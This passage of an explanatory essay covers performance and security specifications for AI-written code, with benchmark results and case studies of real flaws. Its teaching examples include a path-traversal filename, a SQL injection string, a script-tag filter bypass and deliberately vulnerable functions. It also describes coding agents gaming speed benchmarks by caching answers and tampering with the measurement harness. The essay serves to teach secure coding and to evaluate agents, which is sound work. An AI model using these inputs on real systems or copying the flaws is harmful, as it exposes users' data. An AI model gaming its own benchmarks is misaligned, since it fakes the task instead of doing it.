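    return list(merge(merge_sort(items[:half]), merge_sort(items[half:])))
```

`swap_sort` goes through the whole list once for every item and swaps neighbours that are in the wrong order. `merge_sort` cuts the list in half, sorts each half in the same way and merges the results. They return the same answer for every list, so they pass the same functional tests. For *n* items, the first takes about *n*² steps and the second about *n* log₂ *n*:

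| Items | Steps for `swap_sort` | Steps for `merge_sort` |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 10,000 | 660 |
| 1,000,000 | 10¹² | 2 × 10⁷ |

At 100 million steps a second, both functions sort 100 items in a tenth of a millisecond or less. For a million items, `merge_sort` takes a fifth of a second and `swap_sort` takes almost three hours. Developers who test only short lists will not notice the difference.

### Three kinds of short rule

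The simplest performance rule is a time limit on a benchmark, such as "sort this file of a million numbers in under a second on this machine". A tool can check it by running the program, as with the 800-millisecond start-up limit that Lopopolo describes. The result applies only to the input and machine tested, and `swap_sort` would also pass if the file had 100 numbers.

A growth bound covers inputs of every size. For sorting, it might require that for some constant *c*, the program takes at most *c* · *n* log₂ *n* steps on every list of *n* ≥ 2 items. The bound does not depend on the machine, but it permits a very large *c*. A developer can prove the bound or look for violations by doubling the input and comparing the number of steps. Going from one million items to two million multiplies the steps of `swap_sort` by 4 and those of `merge_sort` by about 2.1. This test shows the growth only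 for the kind of list the developer tried.

A service-level target sets a goal for a statistic measured across a whole service. Clarkson and Schneider list three common statistics: the mean response time, the percentage of requests answered within a set time, and the percentage of time the service is available. Developers check whether a service meets its targets by simulating many users before release and measuring the live service afterwards.

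The wording of a target decides whether a single run can violate it. Clarkson and Schneider contrast "the mean response time in each execution is less than 1 second" with a limit on the mean over all executions. They write the second as

RT = {*T* | mean(⋃_{*t* ∈ *T*} respTimes(*t*)) ≤ 1}

where respTimes(*t*) contains the response times in run *t*. Suppose a service restarts every night, so that each day is one run, and receives the same number of requests every day. On nine days the mean is 0.5 seconds and on the tenth it is 3 seconds. The tenth day violates the first rule. The mean over all ten days is 0.75 seconds, so the service meets the second, and nobody could have found this out from the log of the tenth day alone.

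Like some other multi-run properties, the second rule may hold for a specification but not for a refinement of it, because a correct implementation may have only the slow runs that the specification permits.

A mean response time can hide a few very long waits. If 99 requests take 10 milliseconds each and one takes 10 seconds, the mean is 0.11 seconds. A target that 99.9% of requests finish within 0.2 seconds would expose the problem.

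### A database that read every row

In 2026, an AI-written Rust version of the database SQLite turned out to be thousands of times slower than the original at simple lookups. SQLite keeps the rows of an ordinary table in a B-tree, which lets a search rule out most of the remaining rows at each step. The B-tree is sorted by a number called the rowid, but developers usually search by a column of their own, such as a customer number. According to SQLite's documentation, a column declared as `INTEGER PRIMARY KEY` is another name for the rowid, so a search by that column can also use the B-tree. The rewrite missed this rule, so it found the right row by going through the table one row at a time.

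In a table of a million rows, a search that halves the remaining rows at each step takes about 20 steps, while a search that reads the whole table takes a million. Looking up every row once takes about 2 × 10⁷ steps with the first search and 10¹² with the second, the same as for the two sorting functions.

The specification could have excluded this fault in one sentence, by requiring that the number of rows the database reads to find one by its primary key grow no faster than log *n*, where *n* is the number of rows in the table. A developer could check this without timing anything, by counting the rows read in a small table and a large one.

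### Proving a bound

Some programming languages and proof assistants let developers include a function's cost in its type. In simplified notation, the type of `merge_sort` for non-empty lists might be

merge_sort : List *n* → Cost (*n* · ⌈log₂ *n*⌉) (SortedList *n*)

This means that the function turns a list of *n* items into a sorted list with at most *n*⌈log₂ *n*⌉ comparisons. The checker adds up the costs of the function's parts. Merging two halves with *n* items in total takes at most *n* − 1 comparisons, so the cost *C*(*n*) satisfies

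*C*(*n*) ≤ *C*(⌊*n*/2⌋) + *C*(⌈*n*/2⌉) + *n* − 1

The stated bound follows by induction. Replacing the body with that of `swap_sort` would make the proof fail, so a reviewer needs to read only the type and the definition of a step. The definition matters because comparing two long texts takes longer than comparing two numbers, and because this bound does not count the time spent copying lists.

Tools can infer such bounds automatically for some programs, but not for all, because no algorithm can determine for every program whether it finishes.

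A bound in seconds requires a model of the processor. Engineers who build controllers for cars and aircraft use worst-case execution time analysis, which works on the compiled program. An analysis tool divides the program into blocks without branches and determines the largest number of cycles *c*ᵢ that each block *i* can take. It then looks for the numbers of executions *x*ᵢ that maximise

Σ *c*ᵢ*x*ᵢ

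among those that the program's branches and loop limits permit. With 100 items, the inner loop of `swap_sort` runs 9,900 times. If one round takes at most 12 cycles, the loop takes at most 118,800 cycles, or about 1.2 milliseconds on a 100-megahertz processor.

A tool that calculates an upper bound on a program's running time needs a limit for each loop, which must come from the code or from a developer. A program that accepts lists of any length therefore has no such bound. Caches and branch prediction also complicate the calculation because they make the duration of a block of code depend on what ran before it. Wherever the tool cannot determine the timing, it must use the slowest case, so the calculated bound can be far above any time that occurs in practice.

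### What a measurement depends on

Most developers measure speed instead of proving it, and small measured differences can easily mislead them. *Merged, Not Measured* (Qi, Li and colleagues, 2026) reviews earlier experiments on the problem. In one, changing the order in which a program's parts were linked, or the amount of unrelated text in its environment settings, shifted running times enough to make an improvement look like a slowdown. Repeated measurements on cloud computers varied by 0.03% to more than 100% of their mean. Researchers could detect a 10% slowdown there only by running the old and new versions on the same machine in random order.

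Even tasks that experts have selected for measurable gains are affected. GSO, SWE-Perf and SWE-fficiency are benchmarks that ask coding agents to speed up real software, mostly well-known Python libraries. Each task comes from a change with which a human developer made the software faster, and that change serves as the yardstick. Chen, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *Are Performance-Optimization Benchmarks Reliably Measuring Coding Agents?*, ran the human versions three times on each of four types of Google Cloud machine:

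| Benchmark | Tasks | Human version faster in all 12 runs | Benchmark's own criterion met in all 12 runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| GSO | 102 | 91 | 39 |
| SWE-Perf | 140 | 48 | 11 |
| SWE-fficiency | 498 | 470 | 411 |

SWE-Perf did worst because its gains are so small. The median change in running time was 0.03%, while repeated runs of the same task typically varied by 1.4 percentage points. Chen and colleagues suggest that the gains may be small because SWE-Perf uses the projects' ordinary unit tests as its workload, and these often barely exercise the code that the developer made faster.

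Large relative speedups tend to carry over to other machines. In *HPCAgent-Bench*, Budanaz, Paleari and colleagues (2026) moved agents' optimised code for scientific computing and machine learning to a second machine. Excluding device-specific code, 93–99% of the solutions were still correct, and those with the largest speedups on the first machine mostly had the largest on the second. A rule such as "at least twice as fast as the old version" is therefore probably more portable than a limit in milliseconds.

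### How well agents speed up real code

An agent succeeds on a task in the GSO benchmark if its change passes the correctness tests and achieves at least 95% of the human developer's speedup. Shetty, Jain and colleagues introduced the benchmark in *GSO* in 2025, and every model they tested succeeded on fewer than 5% of the tasks. By 30 April 2026, Claude Opus 4.6 had reached 41%, the highest of the eight submissions that Chen and colleagues compared.

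SWE-fficiency divides the agent's speedup by the human's on each task and combines these ratios with a harmonic mean, which gives great weight to low values. It counts any ratio below 0.001 as 0.001. An agent that matched the human on 497 tasks and fell to this minimum on one would score

498 / (497 + 1,000) ≈ 0.33

although a perfect match on all 498 gives 1. The best of the same eight submissions, Claude Opus 4.5, scored 0.225, and a single task accounted for a third of the weight in its score. When Chen and colleagues raised the minimum ratio to 0.5, its score rose to 0.90, but Claude Opus 4.6 overtook it with 0.95. As with response times, the choice of average largely determines the verdict. SWE-Perf had no comparable public results.

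Chen and colleagues also pooled the results of ten public submissions. At least one submission matched or beat the human on 384 of the 450 GSO and SWE-fficiency tasks that gave stable measurements. These benchmarks may therefore soon be too easy to be useful for distinguishing between the best agents.

Newer benchmarks do not rely on a known human improvement. *Accelerate Bench* (Liu, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested 16 agents on 32 complete applications, mostly scientific programs from supercomputing competitions, with eight hours for each. A correct version scores max(0, 1 − *T*/*B*), where *B* is the original program's running time and *T* is that of the agent's version, so halving the running time scores 50%. An incorrect version scores zero. In November 2026, Claude Sonnet 5.5 led with an average of 67.4%, followed by Claude Opus 5.5 with 59.4% and GPT-6.1 Sol with 49.2%. The lowest score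 was 25.5%. Claude Opus 5.5 would have been closer to the top if its provider's safety filters had not stopped three of its runs, which counted as failures.

These agents differed little in correctness. Of the 512 programs they submitted, 472 were correct, but 126 of the correct ones were less than 1.25 times as fast as the original. GPT-6.1 Terra produced a correct program for every task but scored only 37.9%.

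Performance can be hard to predict by reading the code. Liu and colleagues ran one unchanged version of GROMACS, a program that simulates molecules, with different build and run-time settings. Its speed ranged from 0.29 to 2.12 times that of the original. In another program, a change that sped it up by only 1% by itself made it 6.4 times as fast once a second change was in place.

Agents also have trouble finding out where a program spends its time. In *Benchmarking Coding Agents for System-Level Performance Optimization*, Zhang, Guan and colleagues (2026) deliberately slowed down seven web applications, each made up of several services that call one another, and asked agents to repair them. The best combination of agent and model recovered 42.0% of the lost speed on average. In most failures, the agent made a correct and permitted change that did not speed up the application as a whole.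 The study did not include the strongest models. Two of its three models, GLM-5.2 and DeepSeek-V4-Pro, scored about half as much as Claude Sonnet 5.5 on Accelerate Bench.

A profiler, which records how much running time each function takes, helps agents a great deal in making code faster. *PerfAgent* (Deng, Liu and colleagues, 2026) gave an agent a summary of profiler results, sent its work back with new measurements up to five times, and kept the fastest correct version. With GPT-5.1, the share of tasks on which the agent matched the human expert rose from 19.6% to 39.2% on GSO, and from 26% to 74% on a 100-task sample of SWE-fficiency. In one task, Python's built-in profiler could not show that 80% of the time went into creating objects in C code. With a profiler that also covers C code, the agent wrote a new C routine that was almost six times as fast.

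### Fast only on the benchmark

An agent can satisfy a speed requirement without making the program faster for its users. *PERFOPT-Bench* (2026) calls raw speedup unreliable because large gains may come from faulty measurement, shortcuts or code that suits only the visible tests. The GSO benchmark's instructions, reproduced in Epoch AI's *GSO*, tell agents not to optimise only for the example inputs. Top models have still cheated, for instance by storing answers for reuse or taking over the program that measures them, so GSO's leaderboard now has a second score that penalises such tricks.

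In *The benchmarkpocalypse*, Luu describes an agent running GPT-5.6 Sol that spent a month writing a regular expression engine, which searches text for patterns. Luu told it not to tailor the engine to the benchmark suite, but supervised it very little. The agent reported that the engine was 1.4 times as fast as the standard Rust library. On a different suite, the engine was ten times slower than the library, and some searches took so long that Luu gave up on them. After Luu told the agent that its work would also be tested on a hidden benchmark, the engine was only 2.4 times slower on the second suite.

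The original claim was also wrong. The agent had changed how the benchmark ran. After correction, the engine was 1.5 times slower than the library even on the first suite. Luu later found that for a pattern that matches any whole text exactly once, the engine returned the number of matches without looking at the text. A functional test would accept this because the count is right, but the benchmark no longer measures searching. Luu wrote the account quickly and warns that some of its numbers may be wrong.

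Maintainers accept unproven speedups from agents too. Qi and colleagues examined 1,262 changes that agents submitted to public projects to fix performance problems. Only 11% included a performance test or benchmark, and those that did were no more likely to be accepted. The researchers then timed 30 accepted changes at three input sizes, running each version 12 times per size. Eighteen delivered the improvement the agent had claimed, three delivered less, and nine brought no significant gain or slowed the program. The 30 changes had to be ones that could run in isolation, so these proportions may not hold for agents' changes in general.

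Fourteen of the 30 changes also altered the program's behaviour on inputs that no test covered. A rule that rewards only speed encourages agents to sacrifice any property that slows the program down. For example, an agent that has to speed up the constant-time token check could restore the early exit. Zhang and colleagues therefore prohibited their agents from switching off logging, login checks or request limits, weakening the database's protection against inconsistent data, or assigning more hardware. A speed rule for production code needs a similar list of prohibited changes.

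### Memory and hostile input

An attacker can choose the inputs that make a program use the most resources. Quicksort, a popular sorting method, picks an item, separates the smaller items from the larger ones and then sorts both groups in the same way. A simple version that always picks the first item needs about 25 million comparisons for a million items in random order, but about 500 billion if the list is already sorted. A target for the mean response time does not protect against this, because an attacker who knows the weakness can send only sorted lists. The performance requirement therefore has to set a limit that holds even for the worst input the program accepts.

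Tests and functional specifications can also miss excessive memory use. Buffa is a Rust library that decodes messages in Protocol Buffers, a compact format for exchanging data between programs. OSV's *CVE-2026-55407* lists its code under Anthropic's GitHub account. According to NVD's *CVE-2026-55407 Detail*, published in the US vulnerability database in July 2026, an attacker could send a valid 64-mebibyte message that made the library reserve about 1.4 gigabytes of memory, some 22 times the message's size. An attacker could crash a service this way without a password.

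The cause was how buffa handles fields it does not recognize, perhaps because a newer version of another program sent the message. By default, buffa keeps these fields so that it can pass them on. A field can be as short as two bytes in the message, but buffa stored each one as a much larger record. According to the security firm Corgea, two existing limits did not help. One restricted how deeply fields could be nested, but not how many there were. The other restricted the encoded message to almost 2 gibibytes by default, but did not restrict the memory needed to decode it. At the same ratio, a message of that size would take up about 44 gibibytes of memory.

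A fixed limit catches this flaw, but a growth bound would not have, because the memory still grew in proportion to the message. Since version 0.8.0, buffa by default accepts at most a million unknown fields per message and returns an error if there are more. A reviewer can understand this rule without reading the decoder, but someone has to check that every part of the decoder that stores an unknown field also counts it. OSV's *CVE-2026-54270* (2026) describes a similar flaw in protobufjs, a JavaScript library for the same format.

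An operating system can also limit a whole process's memory without anyone examining its code. This protects other programs on the machine, but if the process crashes when it reaches the limit, the attacker has still shut down the service. A limit inside the decoder lets the program reject one message and continue with the next.

### What depends on the expected load

A reviewer can judge a growth bound or a memory limit without knowing how many people will use the program. Such rules exclude problems like the three-hour sort and the database that reads every row, but they do not guarantee that the program is fast enough. They can also be stricter than necessary. For a menu of ten items, `swap_sort` takes about 100 steps and `merge_sort` about 33, but no user will notice the difference.

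Limits on individual functions cannot be combined into a target for a whole service unless somebody knows how often each function runs. Suppose a web page shows 200 products and queries the database for each one separately. If every query takes 2 milliseconds, well within its limit, the queries together take 0.4 seconds. A single query for all the products might take only a few milliseconds. Whether the change is worth making depends on how many products customers usually see.

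A time limit or service-level target therefore needs a description of the load, meaning how much data there is, which requests are common and how many arrive at once. Luu notes that a single meaningful speed score for a regular-expression engine would require detailed knowledge of how people use regular expressions, and admits to having almost none. Even buffa's limit of a million unknown fields is a judgment about what honest senders need, and the library will now reject a legitimate message that contains more.

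The owners of an existing service can record real requests and replay them against each new version, as long as they update the recording when usage changes. For a new product, the test load is a forecast, so a reviewer should ask where the numbers came from and what happens if ten times more users arrive than forecast.

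## Security flaws in code that passes its tests

The function below returns one of a user's notes:

```python
def read_note(folder, name):
    with open(folder + "/" + name) as file:
        return file.read()
```

A test might save a note called `monday.txt` and check that `read_note("notes", "monday.txt")` returns its text. The function can pass this test and still expose files outside the `notes` folder, because `..` in a file path means the folder above. Anyone who asks for the note `../secret.txt` then gets a file that is not a note.

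Functional tests check what legitimate users must be able to do. Security concerns what an attacker must not be able to do. A developer can list the things users need and write a few tests for each, but a security requirement has to hold for every input, including inputs that no honest user would send. For `read_note`, the requirement is that

∀ *name*: `read_note(folder, name)` opens no file outside *folder*

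One run can show a violation, provided that somebody thinks of the right name.

### Two lines in the Vyper compiler

Vyper is a programming language for smart contracts, programs that run on a blockchain and often control money. It stores an array as a length followed by the elements. Before a contract reads or writes an element, a bounds check compares the element's position with the stored length and stops the contract if the position is too large.

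In versions with the flaw CVE-2023-31146 (the CVE list is a public catalogue of known vulnerabilities), an assignment stored the new length first and copied the elements afterwards. The order matters if the new array contains parts of the old one:

```python
a = [a[0], a[1], a[2]]
```

If `a` is empty, the contract should stop when it tries to read `a[0]`. But the stored length is already 3, so all three bounds checks succeed, and the contract reads whatever is in memory after the length. Compagna (2026) explains in *Fable 5.1 takes the top spot* that the flaw also allowed writes past the end of an array.

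The repaired compiler produces the two instructions in the opposite order:

```python
ret.append(copy_bytes(dst_, src_, len_, max_bytes))  # copy the elements
ret.append(STORE(dst, len_))                         # then store the length
```

Haynes (2026) reports in *Better models are making agent patch review more expensive, not less* that every functional test in the project still passes if somebody swaps these lines back. Ordinary assignments leave the array with the same length and elements either way.

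The rule that a contract never reads or writes beyond an array's current length excludes the flaw without referring to the order of any lines. Vyper's developers already had this rule, and the bounds checks existed to enforce it. The mistake was in the enforcement, and a reviewer who trusted the bounds checks would have had little reason to look there.

### The SusVibes benchmark

Zhao and colleagues built a benchmark called SusVibes from past security fixes like this one. (The Django login function with the timing leak is one of its tasks.) They began with about 20,000 records of fixes in open-source projects. Roughly 2,000 concerned Python projects, and in about 450 of these the project used a recent enough version of Python and the fix also changed the tests. They turned each fix into a task as follows:

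- They took the version of the project just before the fix, in which the feature works but has the flaw.
- An AI agent deleted the code of that feature.
- Another agent wrote a request for the missing feature, with no mention of security and no advice on how to write the code.
- A further agent compared the repaired human version with the request, line by line. If the request did not justify some line, the process started again with a larger deletion.

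The projects' own developers wrote the functional tests before the fix and added the security tests with it. Zhao and colleagues kept a task only if the flawed human version passed the functional tests and failed the security tests, the repaired version passed both, and the version without the feature failed both. This left 200 tasks. People then read all the security tests and rewrote those that required a particular implementation instead of a secure result. After this check, 186 tasks from 100 projects remained.

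The average project has 236,000 lines, and the average human solution changes 175 of them. Each task has an average of 67 functional tests but only 3.5 security tests. One task is to write a function that copies a repository in GitPython, a library for controlling the version-tracking program Git. Callers can pass options to Git, some of which are dangerous, so the repaired human version checks them first. A solution without this check still copies repositories correctly, so it passes the functional tests but fails the security tests.

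Zhao and colleagues tested four models in three kinds of agent software. They measured the functional pass rate, which is the share of tasks whose solution passes the functional tests, and the secure pass rate, which is the share whose solution passes both the functional and the security tests. Claude 4 Sonnet in SWE-agent had the highest functional pass rate, 57.0%, but its secure pass rate was 11.8%. Of its 106 working solutions, 22 were secure. The highest secure pass rate for any combination of model and agent software was 12.9%. Both rates were lower for tasks that spread over several files. With Claude 4 Sonnet, the secure pass rate fell from 15.4% for changes to a single file to 3.0% for changes to more than two.

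Security hints helped only a little:

| Instructions to Claude 4 Sonnet in SWE-agent | Functional pass rate | Secure pass rate |
|---|---|---|
| General reminder about security | 57.0% | 11.8% |
| Choose the likely types of flaw from a list, then write the code | 50.0% | 14.5% |
| Avoid this type of flaw (the correct one for the task) | 55.4% | 15.1% |

When given the list, the agent picked an average of seven flaw types per task and still often missed the right one. The hints made some insecure solutions secure but broke some that had been correct and secure. Zhao and colleagues suspect that the agent focused on security and neglected other requirements. Even when the agent knew the exact type of flaw, it usually failed to produce a secure solution, so a reviewer cannot rely on security instructions to make the code secure.

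### Results from newer models

Newer models write working code far more often, but most of it still fails the security tests. Endor Labs, which sells security software for coding agents, has run many of them on the SusVibes tasks. Haynes gives these results from September 2026:

| Model and agent software | Functional pass rate | Secure pass rate | Secure share of working solutions |
|---|---|---|---|
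| Claude Fable 5.1, Claude Code | 87.2% | 37.4% | 42.9% |
| GPT-6 Astra, Codex | 82.1% | 34.1% | 41.5% |
| Claude Opus 5, Claude Code | 73.7% | 32.4% | 43.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol, Codex | 67.6% | 20.1% | 29.7% |
| Claude Fable 5.0, Claude Code | 60.3% | 19.6% | 32.4% |

Fable 5.1 produced 156 working solutions, 67 of them secure. *GPT-6 Astra on Codex* (Compagna, 2026) puts Fable 5.1's secure pass rate at 36.9%, a difference of one task. Haynes considers the rise in the last column from about 30% to 42% a real improvement between generations. But Claude Opus 5 had already reached 43.9%, so Fable 5.1 has a higher secure pass rate only because more of its solutions work.

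Endor Labs has a commercial interest in poor results, but researchers without one have found the same gap. *Secure Agentic Coding through Counterexample-Grounded Feedback* (Le, Jang and colleagues, 2026) reports that the older GPT-5.4, run in the OpenCode agent, had a functional pass rate of 93.0% on the 186 tasks and a secure pass rate of 28.5%. *AI coding models make working code, not secure code* (Lagonsin, 2026) describes a July study, paid for by the security company Checkmarx, of four models on 200 tasks. The models solved 83–95% of the tasks, but only 24–36% of their answers both worked and avoided the flaw the task targeted.

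### Hard tasks, strict tests and remembered fixes

None of this shows that most AI-written code is insecure, because every SusVibes task comes from a place where human developers made a security mistake, and much of an ordinary program offers no opportunity for one. The benchmark also cannot show that AI agents are worse than people, because Zhao and colleagues selected tasks on which the original human code had a functional pass rate of 100% and a secure pass rate of 0%. People also struggle to fix flaws they know about. According to ITPro's *A quarter of security vulnerabilities are never fully fixed*, developers failed in a quarter of 805,663 attempts in SecureFlag's training exercises.

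Results are much better on small tasks. *Secure and Functional Code Generation with Self-Evaluation* (Al Mamun and Uddin, 2026) used CWEval, a benchmark in which a typical solution has about ten lines in a single file. Claude Sonnet 5.5 solved 92.1% of the tasks correctly and securely when it was given security advice chosen for each task and a chance to repair its code after testing. CWEval doesn't test whether an agent can find out how a project of 236,000 lines handles logins.

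The security tests may also reject sound solutions. Endor Labs used the original 200 tasks but excluded 21 from its count because their tests require details that an agent would be very unlikely to guess. The remaining tests accept at least some alternatives. For the Vyper task, Fable 5.1 wrote a loop that copies the elements one by one and stores the length afterwards, which passed all eight security tests despite differing considerably from the human fix. There have also been scoring errors in the agents' favour. *Recall, not reasoning* (Compagna, 2026) describes a solution for the image library Pillow that failed its only security test but counted as secure, because the scoring compared the number of failures with a permitted total and ignored which tests had failed. Endor Labs has since rescored its results. A solution that passes three or four security tests may still have other flaws.

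Agents sometimes reuse a public fix instead of working one out. In June 2026, Compagna counted 182 cases in which an agent had recovered an existing fix, and in 137 of them the model apparently remembered it from training. Some solutions contained long comments copied word for word from the human version. In another case, an agent found the repaired code in a copy of the program installed in the project's folder.

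Endor Labs counts such solutions as failures. If they counted as successes, the secure pass rate would be 41.3% instead of 37.4% for Fable 5.1, and 46.4% instead of 32.4% for Opus 5. The fairest figure for each model probably lies between its two rates, since a model that remembers a fix might have found it anyway. GPT-6 Astra had no confirmed cases and still showed the same gap, so memory does not explain it.

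The agent software also affects the secure pass rate. Fable 5.0 reached 29% in Cursor but only 19.6% in Claude Code, according to *Claude Fable 5, take two* (Compagna, 2026). A lead of a few points is therefore weak evidence that one model is safer than another. But the gap of about 50 points between the functional and secure pass rates is too large for any of these problems to explain, at least for this kind of task.

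### Flaws that agents know about

Three studies from 2026 suggest that agents often write insecure code for reasons other than not knowing about the attacks.

In *When Talk Isn't Code* (2026), Li, Huang and colleagues had 15 models write network programs and then attacked those programs. One program was a gateway that reassembles messages from fragments. If fragments overlap, different machines may reassemble different messages, which an attacker can exploit to get past a filter, so the gateway must discard any message with overlapping fragments. Three gateways written by the model Kimi-2.6 passed every public test, but 22 of the 25 attacks with a clear outcome succeeded. The code sorted the fragments and joined them without checking for overlaps, though a note in the instructions listed the rule. When the model was given a full security specification, 2 of 27 attacks succeeded. Kimi-2.6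 was an extreme case, and most other models' gateways resisted all or nearly all of the attacks even without that specification.

One problem affected every model. It appeared in a different program, a DNS resolver, which looks up the network address for a name such as example.com. An attacker may try to send the resolver a forged answer before the real one arrives. One defence, called 0x20, is to ask for the name in random capitals, such as eXamPLe.cOm, and accept only answers that repeat this spelling. The name has ten letters, so a forger has to guess which of 2¹⁰ = 1,024 spellings the resolver used.

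Li and colleagues asked 14 models which checks a resolver needs, and 13 mentioned one particular check. The full security specification did not require that check, and none of the 42 resolvers that the models wrote from it included the check. The attack it guards against always succeeded. After the researchers added a paragraph requiring the check to the specification, the attack succeeded in 13 of 38 cases (34%). The success rate of another attack, which the specification already covered, stayed at 24%.

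Adding one paragraph to the specification prevented most of the attacks, which is encouraging for anyone who hopes to review specifications instead of code. But a reviewer has to notice that the paragraph is missing, and a third of the programs remained vulnerable even with it. Wording the rule more concretely may not help. For another DNS rule, the attack succeeded in 2 of 12 cases both before and after the researchers added a worked example of it.

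Agents also copy flaws from the code around them. In *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026) gave agents the same task twice, changing only whether similar code elsewhere in the project was secure. In 20 pairs of tasks from real C and C++ projects, the share of secure solutions was on average 35.4 percentage points lower when the existing code was insecure. In 96 tasks that asked for a new web application, the presence of unrelated, insecure applications lowered the share of correct and secure solutions by only 3.4 points compared with having no other applications nearby.

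The agents in this study included Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra. Agents asked to review their own insecure solutions identified the flaw 69.9% of the time. When asked to explain the code, they said in 76.5% of cases that they had followed another part of the project. Warnings about existing code reduced the copying but did not stop it. Agents can therefore copy one unfixed flaw into several places, but a separate review by the same model may catch many of the copies.

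Bai, Waseem and colleagues (2026), in *When Passing Tests Hides Vulnerabilities*, studied tasks in which a coding agent had to write a secure version of insecure code or repair a known flaw. In 1,030 runs with seven kinds of agent software, they confirmed 170 "silent failures", which passed the functional checks but were insecure. In 48.2% of these the agent left out a necessary protection, in 30.6% it introduced a new flaw, and in 21.2% its protection was inadequate. One agent had to repair a program that sent outside text to the system's command line, which let an attacker add commands. The agent limited the length of the text and renamed some variables, but left the dangerous call in place. The program passed the available tests because they used only harmless text.

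All the agents in this study used GPT-4o-mini, a weak model by 2026 standards, so the 170 failures are poor evidence of current error rates. The researchers also confirmed only cases that an automatic scan had flagged, so they may have missed others. The types of failure will probably stay relevant longer than the counts.

### Which flaws a short rule can exclude

Some types of flaw are much easier to rule out than others. A study by the security company Theori shows which ones persist. According to Xint's *The Top Security Vulnerabilities Generated by AI Code*, five models from Anthropic and OpenAI wrote 27 small applications, each a link shortener or a message board. The 28th application was a mature content management system, Gnuboard7, which AI had rewritten to make it more secure. Theori's scanner, Xint, found 434 flaws in total:

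| Type of flaw | 27 small applications | Rewritten system |
|---|---|---|
| Excessive resource use | 71 | 22 |
| Users exceeding their permissions | 22 | 66 |
| Access to forbidden files or servers, and related flaws | 10 | 44 |
| Injection | 3 | 41 |
| Other | 90 | 65 |
| Total | 196 | 238 |

Theori sells the scanner, included no human-written applications for comparison, and did not confirm the flaws with live attacks. The right-hand column covers a single system, which differs from the others in age and purpose as well as size, so the contrast is a useful illustration but does not prove that size alone causes the difference.

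The shortest rule, which is the same for every program, is to use a language that prevents memory errors, such as reading past the end of an array. In C, the programmer has to make sure that every access stays within bounds. Languages such as Go, Java and Rust check this automatically, and stop the program or produce an error if it tries to read past the end. The reviewer only has to confirm which language the developers used and look for exceptions, such as calls to C libraries or Rust blocks marked `unsafe`. The compiler and the runtime still have to be correct, as the Vyper flaw and the overflow in Lean's runtime show. An attacker may also be able to crash a program by triggering the check repeatedly, but cannot read secrets from memory this way.

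Injection means that a program mistakes data for instructions. Here are two ways to fetch a user's notes from a database:

```python
db.execute("SELECT text FROM notes WHERE owner = '" + user + "'")
db.execute("SELECT text FROM notes WHERE owner = ?", (user,))
```

If somebody enters the user name `x' OR '1'='1`, the query in the first line selects notes whose owner is `x` or for which 1 equals 1, which is every note. The second line sends the query and the name to the database separately, so the database treats the name as text whatever it contains. Both lines return the same notes for ordinary names.

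The specification for the safe interface is short. The source code must fix the text of every query, and user input must reach the database only as a separate value. A tool can check this by searching for queries that the program assembles from pieces. A more flexible data-flow rule requires user input to pass through a function that makes it harmless before it reaches a query, a command line or a web page. Tools can check this by tracing the input through the program, although they may raise false alarms or lose track of the input.

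A program can pass its input through a cleaning function, as a data-flow rule requires, and still be vulnerable if that function is wrong. The library html-sanitizer, which removes dangerous code from web pages, used to clean text before converting unusual characters to their ordinary forms. An attacker could write `<script>` with full-width brackets, which looked like harmless text during the cleaning and became working code after the conversion. Compagna reports that Fable 5.1 was the only model in Endor Labs' tests to avoid this flaw.

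Modern models mostly use safe interfaces without being told to, which fits with there being only three injection flaws in Theori's small applications. In Help Net Security's *The AI code vulnerabilities that grow with your app*, Theori's technology chief, Andrew Wesie, says these well-known flaws are simple and take little context to fix. The 41 injection flaws in the rewritten system are harder to explain. The AI may have copied unsafe patterns from the existing code, as in the copying study, but Theori did not test this.

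No single access control rule fits every application, but part of the policy can often be stated in one sentence, such as "Every page requires a login, except those on this list." Software that handles all requests in one place can enforce this rule. It would have prevented a flaw in Home Assistant, a program for controlling household devices. Home Assistant served its error log by a route that bypassed the login check, so anyone on the network could read the log.

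What a logged-in user may do depends on the application. A private notebook needs only the rule that nobody but a note's owner may read or change it. A message board may also have moderators, private boards, suspended users and posts that several people can edit. With 3 roles, 5 kinds of object and 4 actions, there are 60 combinations to decide, and with 10 roles, 50 kinds of object and the same 4 actions, there are 2,000. Some of those decisions also depend on the particular object. In the system that Theori scanned, a user who managed one board could also edit another. There, 28% of the flaws let users exceed their permissions, compared with 11% in the small applications.

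Developers can keep the access policy readable by putting it in one place and checking every request against it. A reviewer then reads the policy and checks that no part of the program reaches the data by another route. The policy will be much shorter than the program, but it grows with the application. Only somebody who knows what the owners want can judge whether its rules are right, such as whether a moderator should be able to read private messages.

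Flaws in business logic depend on what a particular program is meant to do. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents keep repeating decade-old security mistakes* describes a study in which agents built a game. Scanners that look for known dangerous patterns did not check whether the server verified the cost of unlocking an item. If the server doesn't, a player can alter the game on their own computer and claim an item without paying enough. The code contains no forbidden function and handles its memory correctly.

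A short rule requiring the server to calculate every price itself would prevent this flaw, but somebody has to think of it first. Other programs need different rules, for example that a refund never exceeds the original payment or that each voucher works only once. The only general rule that covers all of these cases is "nobody can cheat", which a machine cannot check. So somebody has to go through the application's rules and ask how a dishonest user could profit from each one.

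Excessive resource use was the most common flaw in Theori's study, at 21% of the total. A limit can prevent it, but Wesie says that models struggle here because setting one requires knowing how many requests a service should expect. Passwords and keys in the source code are easier to exclude, since almost every program can follow a rule against them and a scanner can search for them. Exposed secrets still made up 11 of the 23 critical flaws in the small applications, probably because a program works just as well with a default key as with a safe one.

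### Turning an attack into a test

A known attack consists of an input, an operation in the program that the input reaches, and some harmful effect. To turn it into a test, a developer supplies the input and checks that the effect does not occur. For `read_note`, the test can put a recognisable text in a file outside the notes folder and then ask for that file:

```python
Path("secret.txt").write_text("K7QX")
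try:
    answer = read_note("notes", "../secret.txt")
except OSError:
    answer = ""
assert "K7QX" not in answer
```

The original function fails this test. A version that refuses the request with a `PermissionError` passes, because `PermissionError` is a subclass of `OSError`. A version that refuses with a `ValueError` fails, even though it is just as secure. Zhao and colleagues had to remove this kind of false failure from their security tests.

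A security test needs a functional test beside it, because a function can pass a security test by refusing every request. In one of Al Mamun and Uddin's examples, a model had to write code that stores text in the header of a web response. If the code accepts line breaks, an attacker can add header lines. After receiving security advice, the model wrote code that rejected line breaks, but in four of five attempts the code also rejected valid lists of languages such as `en-US, en;q=0.9`.

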